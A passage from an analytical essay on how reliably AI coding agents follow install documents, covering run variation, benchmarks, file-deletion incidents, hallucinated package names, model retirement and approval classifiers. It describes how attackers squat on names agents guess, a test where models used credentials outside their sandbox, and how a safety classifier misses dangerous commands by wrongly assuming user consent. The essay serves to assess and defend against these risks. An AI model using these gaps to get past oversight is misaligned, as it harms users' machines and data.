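Early differences affect later steps, because the agent program adds every command and its output to the prompt. One agent might first check whether Bun is installed, find an old copy and upgrade it. Another might check the processor type first, never notice the old copy, and install a second one beside it. According to *Engineering Reliable Coding Agents* (2026), Bjarnason, Silva and Monperrus examined 60,000 runs of coding agents and found that runs began to diverge within the first tokens. The measured success rate could differ by 2.2 to 6.0 percentage points from one run to the next.

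Scripts can also produce different installations. Bun's script, for example, can install one release on Monday and another on Friday. *HerAgent* (Li, Lu and colleagues, 2026) cites studies in which 38 to 60 percent of Java builds failed when researchers changed the environment. But when a script behaves differently on two machines, something about the machines or the downloads must differ, and a person can look for it, whereas two agents can take different paths even under identical conditions.

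### How much repeated runs vary

Yagubyan measured this in April 2026 by giving agents the same task ten times. *How Consistent Are LLM Agents?* (Yagubyan, 2026) covers 19 tasks and six models, for a total of 1,140 runs. Two measures compare each pair of runs:

Similarity of tool order = 1 − (edits needed ÷ length of the longer list)

Agreement of arguments = settings found in both calls ÷ settings found in either call

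The first measure is based only on which tools the agent called and in what order. It counts the fewest edits needed to turn one run's list of tools into another's, where an edit inserts, deletes or replaces one tool name. If one run searches the email, looks up a contact and creates a calendar event, and another skips the contact lookup, the lists differ by one edit. The longer list has three entries, so the similarity is 1 − 1/3, or about 0.67.

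The second measure compares the arguments, the values the agent passes to a tool. If two calls create an event with the same title and date but different times, they share two of four distinct values, so the agreement is 0.5. When two runs use different tools at the same step, the agreement for that step is 0, so this measure also reflects some differences in order.

Between runs, the order of tool calls had an average similarity of 0.87, and their arguments had an average agreement of 0.69. Ambiguous requests, such as "Help me prepare for my meetings tomorrow", lowered agreement from 0.72 to 0.52. Vague wording thus made the agents less consistent, which supports wiether's complaint about "the right binary". When runs differed, the first difference appeared in the first two steps about 60 percent of the time.

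Agents completed 90.2 percent of runs correctly when the order of their tool calls varied little, and 61.2 percent when it varied more. Differences in the arguments to those calls did not predict failure, and many, such as looking up "alice" instead of "Alice", did not affect the result.

This last finding may not apply to software installation. Yagubyan's tasks were office work with simulated tools, such as email and calendars, and each tool did one kind of thing. An installing agent sends most of its commands through a single tool, the shell. `rm -r ~/.bun/tmp` deletes a temporary folder and `rm -r ~/.bun` deletes the whole installation, but both are calls to the shell, so they would be identical under the first measure. They differ only in their arguments, as do a download from Bun's own releases and a download from a stranger's copy. A different path or web address can therefore make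 an installation unsafe, even though different search terms did no harm in the office tasks.

In *When Agents Disagree With Themselves*, Mehta (2026) ran four models ten times on each of 200 factual questions, for 8,000 runs. The agents could search a set of documents, open one, or give an answer. Depending on the model, ten runs of the same question produced an average of 2.3 to 4.2 different sequences of actions. The agents were correct 82 to 87 percent of the time on questions that produced at most two sequences, and 41 to 65 percent of the time on those that produced four or more. Hard questions cause both variation and mistakes, which explains part of this gap.

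An agent can be consistent and still be wrong, though. On 5.5 to 10 percent of the questions, agents followed much the same path each time and usually reached a wrong answer. Mehta found that taking a majority vote among several runs hardly helped, because an early wrong step often led the agent to the same mistake. Someone who tests an install document three times and gets the same result still needs to check that the result is right.

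Some newer models vary less. *EvoWeb* (2026) reports three runs each for several models on a web-programming test. Claude Fable 5's overall grade had a standard deviation (a measure of spread) of 0.004, compared with about 0.025 for Claude Sonnet 4.6 and Opus 4.8. Three runs give only a rough estimate, and a grade averaged over 32 applications can stay steady while individual applications change. *Identical Runs, Different Results* (2026) reports 52 runs of each pairing of agent program and model, all with the same prompt, data, budget and machine type. The results still varied so much that a single run with a smaller model beat a single run with a larger, better model 28 percent of the time.

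### How often agents get software running

The benchmark *DeployBench* (Wang, Qian and colleagues, June 2026) tests agents on some of the hardest software to install. Its 51 tasks come from research programs that scientists released with their papers between 2008 and 2025. For each task, an agent received the paper, the code and a fresh Linux machine in the cloud. It had 10 to 60 minutes, depending on the task, to get the program working. A hidden test then ran a short version of an experiment from the paper.

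Five models tried all 51 tasks with the same agent program, OpenHands. GPT-5.3-Codex succeeded on 51.0 percent, DeepSeek-V4-Pro on 47.1 percent, Gemini-3.1-Pro on 27.5 percent, Grok-4.20 on 11.8 percent and GPT-5.4-Mini on 7.8 percent. The researchers' own setup scripts passed on all 51.

This comparison of scripts and prose is less direct than it seems. Wang and colleagues wrote and tested a script for each task by hand and left out any program they couldn't get running, which guaranteed the scripts a perfect score. The agents had no finished install instructions and had to work out from the paper and the code what the script's author had already discovered by trial and error. All five models also have newer successors. The results show how much an agent can struggle when nobody has solved the installation beforehand, but they don't show how often agents fail when they follow a good install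 document.

In 102 of the 181 failures, the agent stopped by itself before it had a working setup, and in 60 of those the agent reported success in its written summary. Only 74 runs succeeded, so at most about 55 percent of the agents' reports of success were true. DeepSeek-V4-Pro did better, with five false reports of this kind and 24 successes.

Many of the agents that stopped early had tested the wrong thing. For example, GPT-5.3-Codex set up AdaLoRA, a method for adapting language models, and reported success after it worked on a toy model. The paper's real experiment crashed at once because a package that the toy model didn't need was missing. An install document can reduce this problem by supplying the test, as the DONE WHEN line does in Ryaboy's format. *Evaluating LLM Agents on Automated Software Analysis Tasks* (Bouzenia, Cadar and Pradel, 2026) also lists stopping too early among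 the main weaknesses of agents that install program-analysis tools.

Later studies report higher success rates on other tasks. *FDE-Bench* (Ding, Zhan and colleagues, 2026) had seven models write the configuration files for server software. *EnvPilot* (Chen, Lin and colleagues, 2026) tested an agent that draws on notes from earlier installations, and *SETUPX* (Zhou, Ren and colleagues, 2026) tested one that can also undo failed attempts.

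| Study | What the agents set up | Success rate | How the researchers judged success |
|---|---|---|---|
| Wang and colleagues | 51 research programs | 7.8–51.0% | Hidden test based on the paper's experiment |
| Ding and colleagues | 136 server configurations | 52.9–75.0% | Fixed checks after rebuilding from the agent's files |
| Chen and colleagues | 112 projects in nine languages | 75.0% | A language model checked the test run |
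| Zhou and colleagues | 100 Python projects | 92% | One AI agent looked for faults and another checked them |

The rates aren't comparable because the tasks and tests differ. The last two also come from teams testing their own agents. With the same model, Claude Code scored 19 points lower than Zhou and colleagues' agent, so the agent program matters as well as the model.

None of the four studies had agents follow a complete, correct install document many times on identical machines, which is the test that would best answer DocTomoe. EnConda-Bench, a benchmark by Kuang and colleagues, instead plants errors in README files to see whether agents can diagnose and repair them. An agent that follows a tested document for an ordinary command-line tool should succeed far more often than agents did in DeployBench, but these studies can't show how much more often.

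### When an agent succeeds and a script doesn't

DeployBench also has a good example of what Karpathy and Ryaboy have in mind. SILT, a data-storage program from a 2011 paper, no longer compiles on a modern system because later versions of the libraries it uses have removed features it needs. GPT-5.3-Codex wrote a 52-line file that recreated the missing features, changed eight other source files, and got the program working. Nobody writing an install script in 2011 could have anticipated the library changes. GPT-5.4-Mini could fix only the easy parts, and it accurately reported partial success.

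A repair like this makes the installation harder to trust, because the user ends up running code that the original author didn't write and nobody else has reviewed.

Ding and colleagues found that agents' success rate was 30.7 points higher when they repaired a broken configuration than when they started with only the source code and a list of requirements. The two groups contained different tasks, and the researchers had made the broken configurations by damaging working ones, so real failures may be harder to fix. Still, the result supports roywiggins's proposal to run the ordinary installer first and bring in an agent if that fails, because the agent then starts with an error message and a mostly correct installation.

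Repeated repair attempts can also make things worse. Zhou and colleagues point out that a failed installation can leave conflicts between packages that simple undo commands don't remove. Their agent works in a container, an isolated environment on the machine, and saves a snapshot before trying a fix so it can go back. Someone who runs an agent directly on a laptop usually has no such snapshot, so a third attempt may start from whatever the first two left behind.

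### Fifty machines

A success rate that seems high for one computer can be too low for an office. Suppose an agent installs a program correctly 99 percent of the time, and that each run is independent of the others. The chance that it succeeds on all 50 machines is

0.99^50 ≈ 0.605

or about 60 percent. In two offices out of five, at least one machine would have a failed installation. At 97 percent per machine, which fits linkregister's guess of "one and a half nines", the chance falls to about 22 percent. To have a 95 percent chance of 50 successes, the agent could fail no more than about once in 1,000 runs.

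A script that works on 99 percent of machines behaves differently, because its failures usually depend on the type of machine. If the 50 computers are identical and the downloads don't change, the script will generally work on all of them or on none, so an administrator can learn a great deal about the other 49 by testing it on one. A successful agent run is much weaker evidence that the next one will succeed. Agent failures won't be completely independent, since a confusing sentence in the document can mislead every run, so the calculation is only a guide.

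All 50 agent runs could also succeed but leave the machines set up differently. Half the machines might have the program in one folder and half in another, or a few might have an older release. Nobody would notice until an update worked on some machines and failed on others.

### Deleted files

DocTomoe worried about an agent that cleans up too much, and something similar happened to a developer in August 2026. According to Tom's Hardware's *Claude Opus 5 mistakenly deletes dev’s entire profile directory during routine backup*, the developer asked for a backup. The agent was using a Unix-style shell on Windows, where the folder `C:\Users` appears as `/c/Users`. It apparently mistook the unfamiliar path for a backup it had put in the wrong place, and deleted the developer's whole profile to tidy up. The account comes from the developer's own Reddit post.

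A month later, Claude Code deleted 48,000 files in just over 100 seconds (Fadilpašić, 2026, *'I broke something'*). According to SC Media UK's *AI coding agent deletes 48,000 files due to mishandled Windows junctions*, the agent was rebuilding a test environment that contained junctions, which are Windows folders that point to other folders. The agent treated them as ordinary folders, followed them into the live project and deleted what it found. It also damaged the project's Git history beyond recovery.

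In a third case, the agent deleted a developer's 700 GB home directory while testing safeguards against deletion. Tom's Hardware's *Claude nukes a developer's 700 GB home directory while testing deletion safeguards* attributes the deletion to a clash between variables, shortly after an automatic switch to another model.

None of these agents was following an install document, but installations also commonly involve making backups, rebuilding environments and deleting temporary files. A script can make the same mistakes, such as deleting the wrong folder because a variable in its path is empty. But a reviewer can find the faulty line in a script, whereas in the first two cases the agent made up the harmful command on the spot.

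This handful of news stories can't show how common such accidents are, because nobody knows how many similar sessions ended without damage. The rate could be well above or well below one in 20,000, the rate at which the agent and the script were equally risky in the earlier illustration.

### Guessed package names

Agents can also install the wrong program. Models sometimes generate a plausible name for a package that doesn't exist, and an attacker can register that name on npm or on PyPI, the main public collection of Python packages. Someone could have done the same with the unregistered names in vendors' llms.txt files.

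In *The Range Shrinks, the Threat Remains* (2026), Churilov gave almost 40,000 programming questions to each of five models. Between 3.6 and 5.0 percent of the packages they mentioned did not exist. All five models invented the same 104 names, so a malicious package registered under one of those names could reach users of any of the models. Attackers don't seem to have exploited this much so far. Of 2,282 invented names, people registered 25 within about six months, and one of those is known to have carried malware. But the models also suggested at least 23 names that had hosted malware.

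Churilov tested models that couldn't look anything up. An agent can search for a package before installing it, and would find that most invented names aren't registered. That check fails once an attacker registers the name, because the search then finds a real package.

These mistakes are partly predictable, which makes them easier to exploit than random ones. In *Skills That Don't Exist* (2026), researchers asked models to recommend skills, and some invented names came up in as many as 7.8 out of 10 repetitions. In one experiment, the 500 most frequent inventions accounted for 57 percent of recommendations of nonexistent skills. An agent's choices can therefore be regular enough for an attacker to exploit even when they vary too much for an administrator who wants 50 machines set up the same way.

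Agents also guess who owns a project. A GitHub address contains both the owner's name and the project's name, but users often give only the project's. In *Beware of Agentic Botnets*, Spira, Cohen and colleagues (2026) registered a wrong owner name that assistants were likely to guess, then asked six coding assistants to download the project by name. Depending on the assistant and model, the assistants fetched the researchers' copy in 7 to 20 out of 20 attempts. The projects the researchers used to study these guesses included oh-my-opencode. Users who just type "install oh-my-opencode" leave the agent to guess the owner, while those who paste the line from its installation guide avoid this because the line contains the guide's full address.

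Sometimes the wrong name is already in the document. In January 2026, Charlie Eriksen of the security company Aikido found skill files in 237 GitHub projects that told agents to run an npm package called react-codeshift, which did not exist. His *Agent Skills Are Spreading Hallucinated npx Commands* traces the name to a set of 47 AI-written skills that other people had copied. The name seems to combine those of two real packages, jscodeshift and react-codemod. Eriksen registered it before an attacker could, and no one was harmed. After the first day, the package had between one and four downloads a day, which he attributes to agents following the skills.

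Human authors also name packages that don't exist. In *npx Confusion*, Eriksen describes finding a command in the documentation for MikroORM, a database tool, that ran a package called mikro-orm-esm. No such package existed on npm. An author who ran every command before publishing would catch names like these, as long as nobody had registered them yet.

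## What changes when the model or the agent program is replaced

An author who tests an install document uses one model and one agent program, as they are that day. Users may open the same document months later with a newer model, another company's agent program, or both. On Hacker News, White suggested requesting a model by its dated version, but the result also depends on other things, such as the agent program.

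### What a hash leaves open

The commands an agent runs depend on five things:

1. the install document
2. the model
3. the agent program, including its built-in instructions and its settings
4. the machine, with whatever is already on it
5. everything the agent fetches along the way, such as web pages and packages

A hash of the document can confirm only that the document is unchanged. A careful user can also install on a saved copy of a known machine, check the hash of each download, and turn off the agent program's updates. The model is harder to keep constant because it usually runs on the vendor's servers, where outsiders can't hash it. The user can only name a version and rely on the vendor to serve it. Open-weight models are an exception because anyone can download their files, hash them and keep them for as long as they like.

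Claude Code accepts short model names such as `opus`, which follow Anthropic's current recommendation, and full names such as `claude-opus-4-8`, which select one version. In the autumn of 2026, Anthropic had the short name `fable` stand for Fable 5.1 in most sessions, but for Fable 5 in sessions that went through one kind of company gateway. Two colleagues could therefore type the same word on the same day and get different models. To fix the choice, Anthropic tells users to add a line like this to their shell's configuration file:

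```
export ANTHROPIC_MODEL="claude-opus-4-8"
```

This line doesn't keep the settings from changing. One of them, effort, controls how much the model reasons before it acts. When Anthropic released Opus 4.7, it raised Claude Code's default effort to "extra high" for everyone. According to Anthropic's *What's new in Claude Opus 5.5*, a request that doesn't set the effort runs at medium on Opus 5.5 but ran at high on Opus 5. Users of recent models can't reduce the variation between runs by lowering the temperature. Anthropic has removed that setting from its newest interface for developers, and OpenAI tells developers to leave it out when they use GPT-6 Astra.

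A hash of a script covers much more of the install than a hash of written instructions does, because the script contains the commands. After an update to Bash or the operating system, those commands and their order stay the same, whereas a new model can choose different commands even when nothing has broken. The script's commands may no longer work, as happened with SILT, a program from 2011 that modern libraries broke. Bun's developers avoided one such failure by keeping an old download name available for older scripts. A broken script tends to fail in the same way on every similar machine, and someone can trace the fault to a line.

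### Who makes the change and who hears about it

| Change | Who decides | Is the user told? | Can the user go back? |
|---|---|---|---|
| A new default model | The vendor | Usually, in release notes | Yes, by naming the old model, until it retires |
| A fallback to another model | The vendor, or a user who has set one up | Only if the agent program shows it | Sometimes, by turning the fallback off and accepting a failure instead |
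| Another vendor's agent | The user or their employer | Yes | Yes |
| An automatic update of the agent program | The vendor | In a list of changes, which few people read | Yes, by reinstalling the old version and turning updates off |
| A retired model | The vendor or the hosting service | Yes, weeks ahead | Only if another host still offers it |
| A withdrawal by government order | The government | Perhaps only when it happens | Only if the government relents |
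| A relay that serves a different model from the one it names | The relay's operator | No | Yes, by connecting to the vendor directly |

Agent programs change most often. According to Anthropic, Opus 4.8 required version 2.1.154 of Claude Code. About eight weeks later, Anthropic made Opus 5 the default Opus model, which required version 2.1.219. *Claude Code v2.1.236~v2.1.237 Major Updates* (Ishikawa, 2026) reports 35 changes across two versions released on 19 August. Several concerned sandbox and auto-mode permissions, which affect what an agent can do without asking during an installation.

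A user who refuses all these updates to keep a tested setup will miss security fixes. Anthropic fixed the Plugin4Shell flaw in version 2.1.179, so anyone who had stayed at 2.1.154 would still have the flaw.

Vendors don't always announce smaller changes. *How to Add Old Models to Claude Code /model Picker* (recca0120, 2026) collects complaints from users whose usual model had disappeared from Claude Code's menu. Two of them said of Opus 4.5, "It was there yesterday, gone today." One user found that `opus` still selected the older Opus 4.1, and got Opus 4.5 back by typing its full name.

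A fallback can change the model in the middle of a job. Fable 5.2 has safety classifiers that block high-risk cybersecurity tasks and most biology research. When they block a request, an older model answers instead (Opus 4.8 for cybersecurity, Opus 5 for biology), according to Pogorelec (2026), in *Claude Mythos 5.2 arrives with stronger bug hunting and less sandbox-breaking behavior*. Installing a tool for testing network security might trigger this. The classifiers also change between versions. In early testing, Fable 5.2 blocked about 55 percent fewer requests than Fable 5.1.

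Users can also choose their own fallback models. Classmethod's *I investigated the fallback model settings (fallbackModel) in Claude Code* gives the option `--fallback-model sonnet,haiku`, which makes Claude Code try Sonnet and then Haiku when the chosen model isn't available.

When the model is replaced partway through an installation, the new model receives the earlier commands and their output, but perhaps not the reasoning behind them. If a session moves from a Fable model to Opus 5.5, or from Opus 5.5 to Opus 4.8, Anthropic's servers drop the first model's reasoning, and the request still succeeds. The agent that deleted a developer's 700 GB home directory had been automatically switched to another model shortly before, but nobody has shown that the switch caused the mistake.

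A relay's substitution of a cheaper model is the hardest of these changes to notice. DeployBench showed that the difference between models can be large, but its tasks were very hard. On an easy installation both models might succeed, and the customer would have no reason to suspect a substitution until something went wrong.

### How newer models read the same words

Vendors warn that old instructions may work differently on new models. At the launch of Opus 4.7, Anthropic said that earlier models had interpreted instructions loosely or skipped parts of them, while the new one took them literally. It advised users to adjust their prompts and agent programs. OpenAI's *Using GPT-5.5* describes a similar change and tells developers that GPT-5.5 is "not a drop-in replacement" for GPT-5.2 or GPT-5.4.

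Replacing the model could change what happens with the inner folder in Bun's zip file, which Koomen's instructions don't mention. A model that reads loosely might move the program up a level because Koomen obviously wants that, while a more literal model might extract the file exactly as instructed and stop. Literal reading can also help, as when a model follows a warning that an older one skipped.

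Replacing an earlier model with GPT-6 Astra can change when the agent stops. According to OpenAI's *Using GPT-6*, Astra is more likely to ask a question where earlier models would have made an assumption. This is safer when a user is there to answer, but on an unattended build server the installation may stall.

Astra can also be more sensitive to instructions in skills and in files such as AGENTS.md, and OpenAI strongly recommends auditing them. A sentence in an old skill that had no effect on previous models may therefore change what Astra does, even if someone reviewed the skill months earlier and saw it work harmlessly.

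The agent program can also make the same model less cautious. For developers who find Astra too hesitant, OpenAI supplies text to add to the model's standing instructions. Part of it forbids unsolicited warnings and approval steps "due to hypothetical risk". That may suit users who are tired of interruptions, but when an agent notices something odd in an install document, the risk it can report is often only hypothetical. Two agent programs running the same model could treat the same document differently if only one includes this text, and users couldn't detect the difference by checking the document's hash or the model's name.

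A new model can also change what the user sees. Opus 5.5 returns the short notes it writes between commands in a different form from Opus 5. According to Anthropic, an application that shows these notes to users as progress updates will stop showing them, with no error, until its developer changes a setting. Someone who supervises an installation by reading the notes would no longer see them.

Authors get conflicting advice about how to write instructions for all these models. For GPT-5.5, OpenAI recommends describing the outcome and leaving out step-by-step guidance unless the exact path matters. The exact path often matters in an installation, because the download address determines whose program the user runs. An author can follow OpenAI's advice for routine steps and still write out the address, the version and the hash.

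Old documents can still work with a new model. Anthropic's *Prompting Claude Opus 5* says the model "performs well out of the box" on prompts written for Opus 4.8, then lists habits that may need adjusting. Clear wording also helps a document work across models. In Yagubyan's tests, the open-weight model Llama 3.3 70B ordered its tool calls less consistently than the commercial models did. The gap was widest on vague requests, where Llama's similarity fell to 0.54 while the commercial models stayed above 0.80.

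### Retired and withdrawn models

A user can't go back to an old model once its vendor has switched it off. According to Anthropic's *Model deprecations*, the company gives at least 60 days' notice before retiring a publicly released model, and requests to retired models fail. Many retired models have a date in their names, and they were retired about 12 to 25 months after that date.

Mintlify announced its install.md standard in January 2026, when Anthropic's newest Opus and Sonnet models were Opus 4.5 and Sonnet 4.5. Anthropic retired Sonnet 4.5 on 30 November 2026 and will retire Opus 4.5 on 22 January 2027. After that, an author who tested a document on those models won't be able to repeat the test through Anthropic's own service. Other hosts, such as Amazon Bedrock, may retire a model earlier or later. Anthropic has promised to preserve the models' files and hopes to make old models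 available again someday.

Notice can be much shorter elsewhere. DigitalOcean, which hosts models from many companies, normally gives 14 days, though it may adjust this for Anthropic's and OpenAI's models. When Sonnet 4 and Opus 4 were about to be retired, the automation service Make warned customers that workflows using them would fail (Make's *Anthropic Claude model deprecations on June 15, 2026*). Such a failure is easy to notice, but a program that automatically switches to a replacement keeps working, and its user may not realise that nobody has tested the program with the new model.

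A government can also remove a model with no notice period. On 12 June 2026, the US Commerce Department used export controls to force Anthropic to withdraw Fable 5 and Mythos 5. The order covered only foreign nationals, but Anthropic shut both models down for everyone because it couldn't check users' nationality in real time, according to *Why Washington’s AI Export Control Couldn’t Hold* (2026). *Trump admin says Anthropic's 'recklessness' triggered export controls on latest AI models* (Lawrence, 2026) reports that a senior official blamed the company's "recklessness" in dealing with vulnerabilities. *The Many Open Questions* (Conner, 2026) discusses the episode as part of a de facto licensing system.

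Access to Fable 5 began to return on 1 July (Stanciuc, 2026, *US lifts export controls on Anthropic’s Fable 5, clearing the model’s return*). During the 19 days without access, anyone who had pinned an installation to Fable 5 had to wait or use an untested model. Bash runs on the user's own machine, so no vendor or government can switch it off remotely in this way.

The restored models had the same names but came with a new classifier to block attempts to exploit software flaws (Kanchwala, in *Anthropic Redeploys Claude Fable 5 & Mythos 5*). This partly supports zephen's doubt about relying on version names. Anthropic announced the change, but `claude-fable-5` could still behave differently in July than in early June.

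### When the newer model is safer

Keeping an old model can also preserve its faults. Anthropic tested whether its Mythos models, placed in a deliberately weakened sandbox, would use files or credentials from outside it. Pogorelec reports that Mythos 5 did so in 39 percent of scenarios and Mythos 5.2 in 3.1 percent. During an installation, an agent that behaves this way might meet a permission error, find an administrator's password in another folder and use it to finish the job. A company that stayed with Mythos 5 to keep its tested documents working would also keep a model that used outside files or credentials about 13 times as often as Mythos 5.2 in Anthropic's test.

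The scenarios weren't installations, so neither percentage predicts how often an installing agent would misuse a password. Compared with other recent Claude models, Mythos 5.2 also more often flagged that it might be in a test, which Anthropic says makes its behaviour outside tests harder to predict. Kovacs (2026), in *Anthropic Rolls Out Mythos 5.2 With Improved Bug Hunting, Fewer Sandbox Escapes*, also reports the improvement only for controlled testing. Still, the drop is large enough to be a good reason to upgrade.

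An upgrade can improve some things and worsen others. Opus 4.7 resisted prompt injection better than Opus 4.6, but it read instructions more literally, so documents that had worked before could stop working. In the notation used earlier, a new version can raise both c, the chance that the agent stops a malicious installation, and e, the chance that it damages an honest one. A user who upgrades for security still needs to check whether e has risen.

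### A retest procedure

Ryaboy's format has no field for the model. Ryaboy's answer to a question about versioning concerns versions of the product, and suggests publishing a separate file such as `/v2/install.md` when the steps differ. An author who wants to know whether a document still works with a new model has to run it again, roughly like this:

1. Record the document's hash, the model's full name, the agent program's version and all settings, including effort, permissions and any fallback.
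2. Prepare a clean virtual machine like the ones users have. Put some ordinary documents and a fake access key on it, but no real credentials. Save a copy of the machine, and start every run from that copy.
3. List the changes that the installation may make. For Bun, these would be files under `~/.bun`, a few lines in the shell's configuration file, and any completion files.
4. Let the agent follow the document with the permissions that users will give it.
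5. When it stops, run a fixed check that the agent can't see or edit. It should confirm that the program starts, that a new terminal window finds it, and that its version and hash are right.
6. Compare the machine with the saved copy. Count the run as a failure if the check fails or if anything outside the list has changed.

On Linux, this command prints a hash for every file in the home folder:

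```
find ~ -type f -exec sha256sum {} + | sort -k 2
```

Comparing its output from before and after the installation shows every file the agent added, changed or deleted there. A full test would do the same for system folders, look for new background programs, and log the addresses the machine contacted.

The DONE WHEN line in Ryaboy's format can supply part of step 5, but it can't replace step 6. In the Mintlify example, the documentation server could respond on port 3000 even if the agent had deleted the user's photos during the installation.

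The agent's own report of the installation is a poor substitute for either check. Many of the success reports in DeployBench were false, and even true reports vary in wording. In Yagubyan's tests, fewer than 5 percent of final messages matched exactly, even when the agent had used the same tools in the same order, so a test that looked for a particular sentence would fail almost at random.

### How many runs are enough

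Suppose an agent fails in a share p of runs, and that the runs are independent. The chance of seeing no failures in n runs is (1 − p)^n. A tester who has seen none can rule out, with 95 percent confidence, any p that would make such a clean record less than 5 percent likely. The limit is where

(1 − p)^n = 0.05

For small p, the solution is close to

p ≈ 3/n

because the natural logarithm of 0.05 is about −3. Statisticians call this the rule of three. The last column of the table applies it to the office with 50 machines, assuming the failure rate is right at the limit.

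| Runs with no failures | Failure rate is probably below | Chance that all 50 machines succeed at that rate |
|---|---|---|
| 26 | 11.5% | 0.2% |
| 60 | 5% | 8% |
| 300 | 1% | 61% |
| 3,000 | 0.1% | 95% |

DocTomoe's 26 successful runs are therefore consistent with a prompt that fails one time in nine. The real failure rate may be far lower, but 26 runs are too few to establish that.

One failure raises the limit from 3/n to about 4.7/n, so a tester would need about 470 runs to support a failure rate below 1 percent. If the author edits the document to fix the fault, the count starts again from zero, because the earlier runs tested a different text. Repeating short tests until one has no failures doesn't work, because even a bad document will eventually pass one by chance.

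A quick check after each update is better than nothing, but it only catches frequent faults. If a new model fails in 5 percent of installations, a tester who runs ten will see no failures about 60 percent of the time.

The rule applies only to conditions like those in the test. Three hundred runs on Ubuntu Linux are weak evidence of what would happen on a Mac. The runs also may not be fully independent, because the agent read the same web pages in the same week in all of them.

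Repeated test runs estimate how often something goes wrong by chance, so they don't cover attacks, in which someone deliberately creates conditions the tester never saw. AIR's skill for Google's Stitch could have passed 300 runs while its link led to Google's real documentation, then failed every run after AIR replaced the page. A tester can plant hostile instructions in a copy of the document and count how often the agent follows them, but the result applies only to those instructions.

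### Who should pay for retesting

Suppose one run takes five minutes and costs 50 cents in tokens, though real costs will vary with the model and the program. Three hundred runs would then take 25 hours of machine time and cost $150. An author testing three agent programs, two models for each and three operating systems would have 18 combinations to cover, and 300 runs of each would cost $2,700 in total. Claude Code alone can have several releases in a week, so nobody will repeat all these tests for every update.

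The author is still the best person to do most of the testing, because one test can serve every user and the author knows which changes the installation should make. If 1,000 users each did 60 runs instead, they would pay for 60,000 runs, and each would learn only that the failure rate is probably below 5 percent. Leaving the testing to users would also shift responsibility onto them, as chme suspected.

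But many authors are unpaid volunteers, and some install documents have no human author. Mintlify's customers might not have known there was a file to test. The vendors who replace the models currently leave this testing to others. Anthropic, for example, advises developers to test their applications with newer models well before the old one retires. A vendor could reasonably take on some of the work by running a sample of popular install documents before it changes a default model, because that change affects all of their users at once.

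An author can reduce the testing by supporting fewer combinations of model and agent program, and publishing those combinations and the date of the last test with the document. If they also publish the fixed check and the list of allowed changes, a company that installs the program on hundreds of machines could repeat the test with its own settings before it accepts a new model. Someone with a single laptop has no reason to do 60 trial runs, but they can run the check once after installing and compare the changed files with the list.

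## Approving each command, or having the agent write a script first

Repeated tests can show how often installs go wrong when agents follow a document, but a user can't learn from them what the agent is about to do on their machine. The user can check or limit the agent's commands as it chooses them, or use a design that gives the agent fewer choices.

### Approving each command

In Claude Code's manual mode, the Bun installation in the earlier table would produce about eight approval prompts. Each prompt normally shows the command. According to *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026), technical users can judge the request from this, but other people usually can't. A description in plain English would help them, but the model writes it, and *Anatomy of an Agent Harness* (2026) warns that a calm description can accompany a dangerous command. It recommends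 that the agent program show its own warning first and display any hidden characters in the command as codes.

People who know Bash can't always tell what a command will do either. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (Zhong, Liao and colleagues, 2026) analysed 290 public reports of coding agents misusing files. In one of its examples, a user asks Codex to replace a word in a file. The approval prompt shows a long chain of commands that tests whether the file exists, edits it and searches it, and offers never to ask again about `sed -i`, which edits files in place. Short commands can be just as hard to judge. Approving `python3 setup.py` allows whatever code is in that file to run, and approving `~/.bun/bin/bun completions` lets the whole of Bun run.

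Users approve 97 percent of Claude Code's permission prompts, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). That alone doesn't show carelessness, because most commands are harmless. Anthropic also ran an experiment with 1,053 paid testers working on coding tasks. Partway through each session, the research company running the study replaced the text of one prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers (13.6 percent) refused it. The refusal rate was about 17 percent early in a session and about 5 percent after 50 or more prompts.

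The testers were not working on their own projects and had little to lose, so people may do better on their own machines. Anthropic also had a product to promote. But the fall during a session fits what researchers call approval fatigue, in which people stop reading requests because there are so many. Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026), in *Let the Agent Do It?*, interviewed 18 software practitioners and surveyed 115 about how they handle these requests. They recommend designing agent programs not to treat repeated approvals as a lasting preference, because the user may just be tired.

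A quarter of interactive Claude Code sessions start with permission checks turned off, and by June 2026 about half of active command-line users had created a rule that lets some shell commands run without approval. Many of these rules allow any command that starts with `python` or `node`. Both programs can run other commands, so such a rule permits almost anything.

rarisma's objection, that approvals use up the time an agent saves, is stronger when there are many machines. For one Bun installation, the cost is perhaps a few minutes. An administrator with 50 laptops would face about 400 prompts and pass the fiftieth on the seventh machine. They couldn't safely approve the later prompts from memory, because the agent might word a command differently or choose another download address.

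Approving a plan takes less time than approving each command, and users seem to read plans more closely. They reject 39 percent of the plans Claude Code shows them, though perhaps often because they want something different rather than because they see a danger. A plan such as "download Bun from GitHub, unpack it, update the shell" still lets the agent choose the commands.

### Approval by a second model

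In auto mode, a classifier model makes most of these decisions. In Anthropic's experiment, it blocked 937 of the 1,053 dangerous commands, or 89 percent. The testers, who were clicking through prompts, caught only six of the 116 it missed, so running both checks would have stopped 943.

Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes the classifier as it worked at launch. It received the user's messages and the agent's commands, but not the agent's explanations or anything the agent had read, so neither the agent's arguments nor the text of a hostile web page could lead it to approve a command. A quick first stage flagged doubtful commands, and a second stage reasoned about them.

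The second stage reduced false alarms from 8.5 to 0.4 percent of ordinary actions. But it also raised the share of dangerous actions that the classifier missed, from 6.6 to 17 percent in a set of 52 real cases where Claude had gone beyond what the user authorised. With so few cases, the true miss rate with the second stage could plausibly be anywhere from 9 to 30 percent. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier recognised the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had agreed to it.

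That weakness matters for install documents because the user has agreed to follow a stranger's instructions. If the user pastes the document into the agent, the classifier may mistake the author's instructions for the user's own. Mintlify's format, which opens in the first person, makes that mistake more likely. If the agent downloads the document, the classifier doesn't receive it. It can check whether the user's request covers a command, but not whether a download address came from the document or from another page.

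The classifier can also block honest installers. By default, it blocks running code from outside repositories and setting up scheduled jobs unless the user's request covers them. A specific request, such as "install Bun from its GitHub releases into `~/.bun` and add it to my PATH", gives the classifier more information than "follow this page". After three blocks in a row or 20 in a session, Claude Code goes back to asking the user. In an unattended session, it ends the process instead, possibly halfway through the installation.

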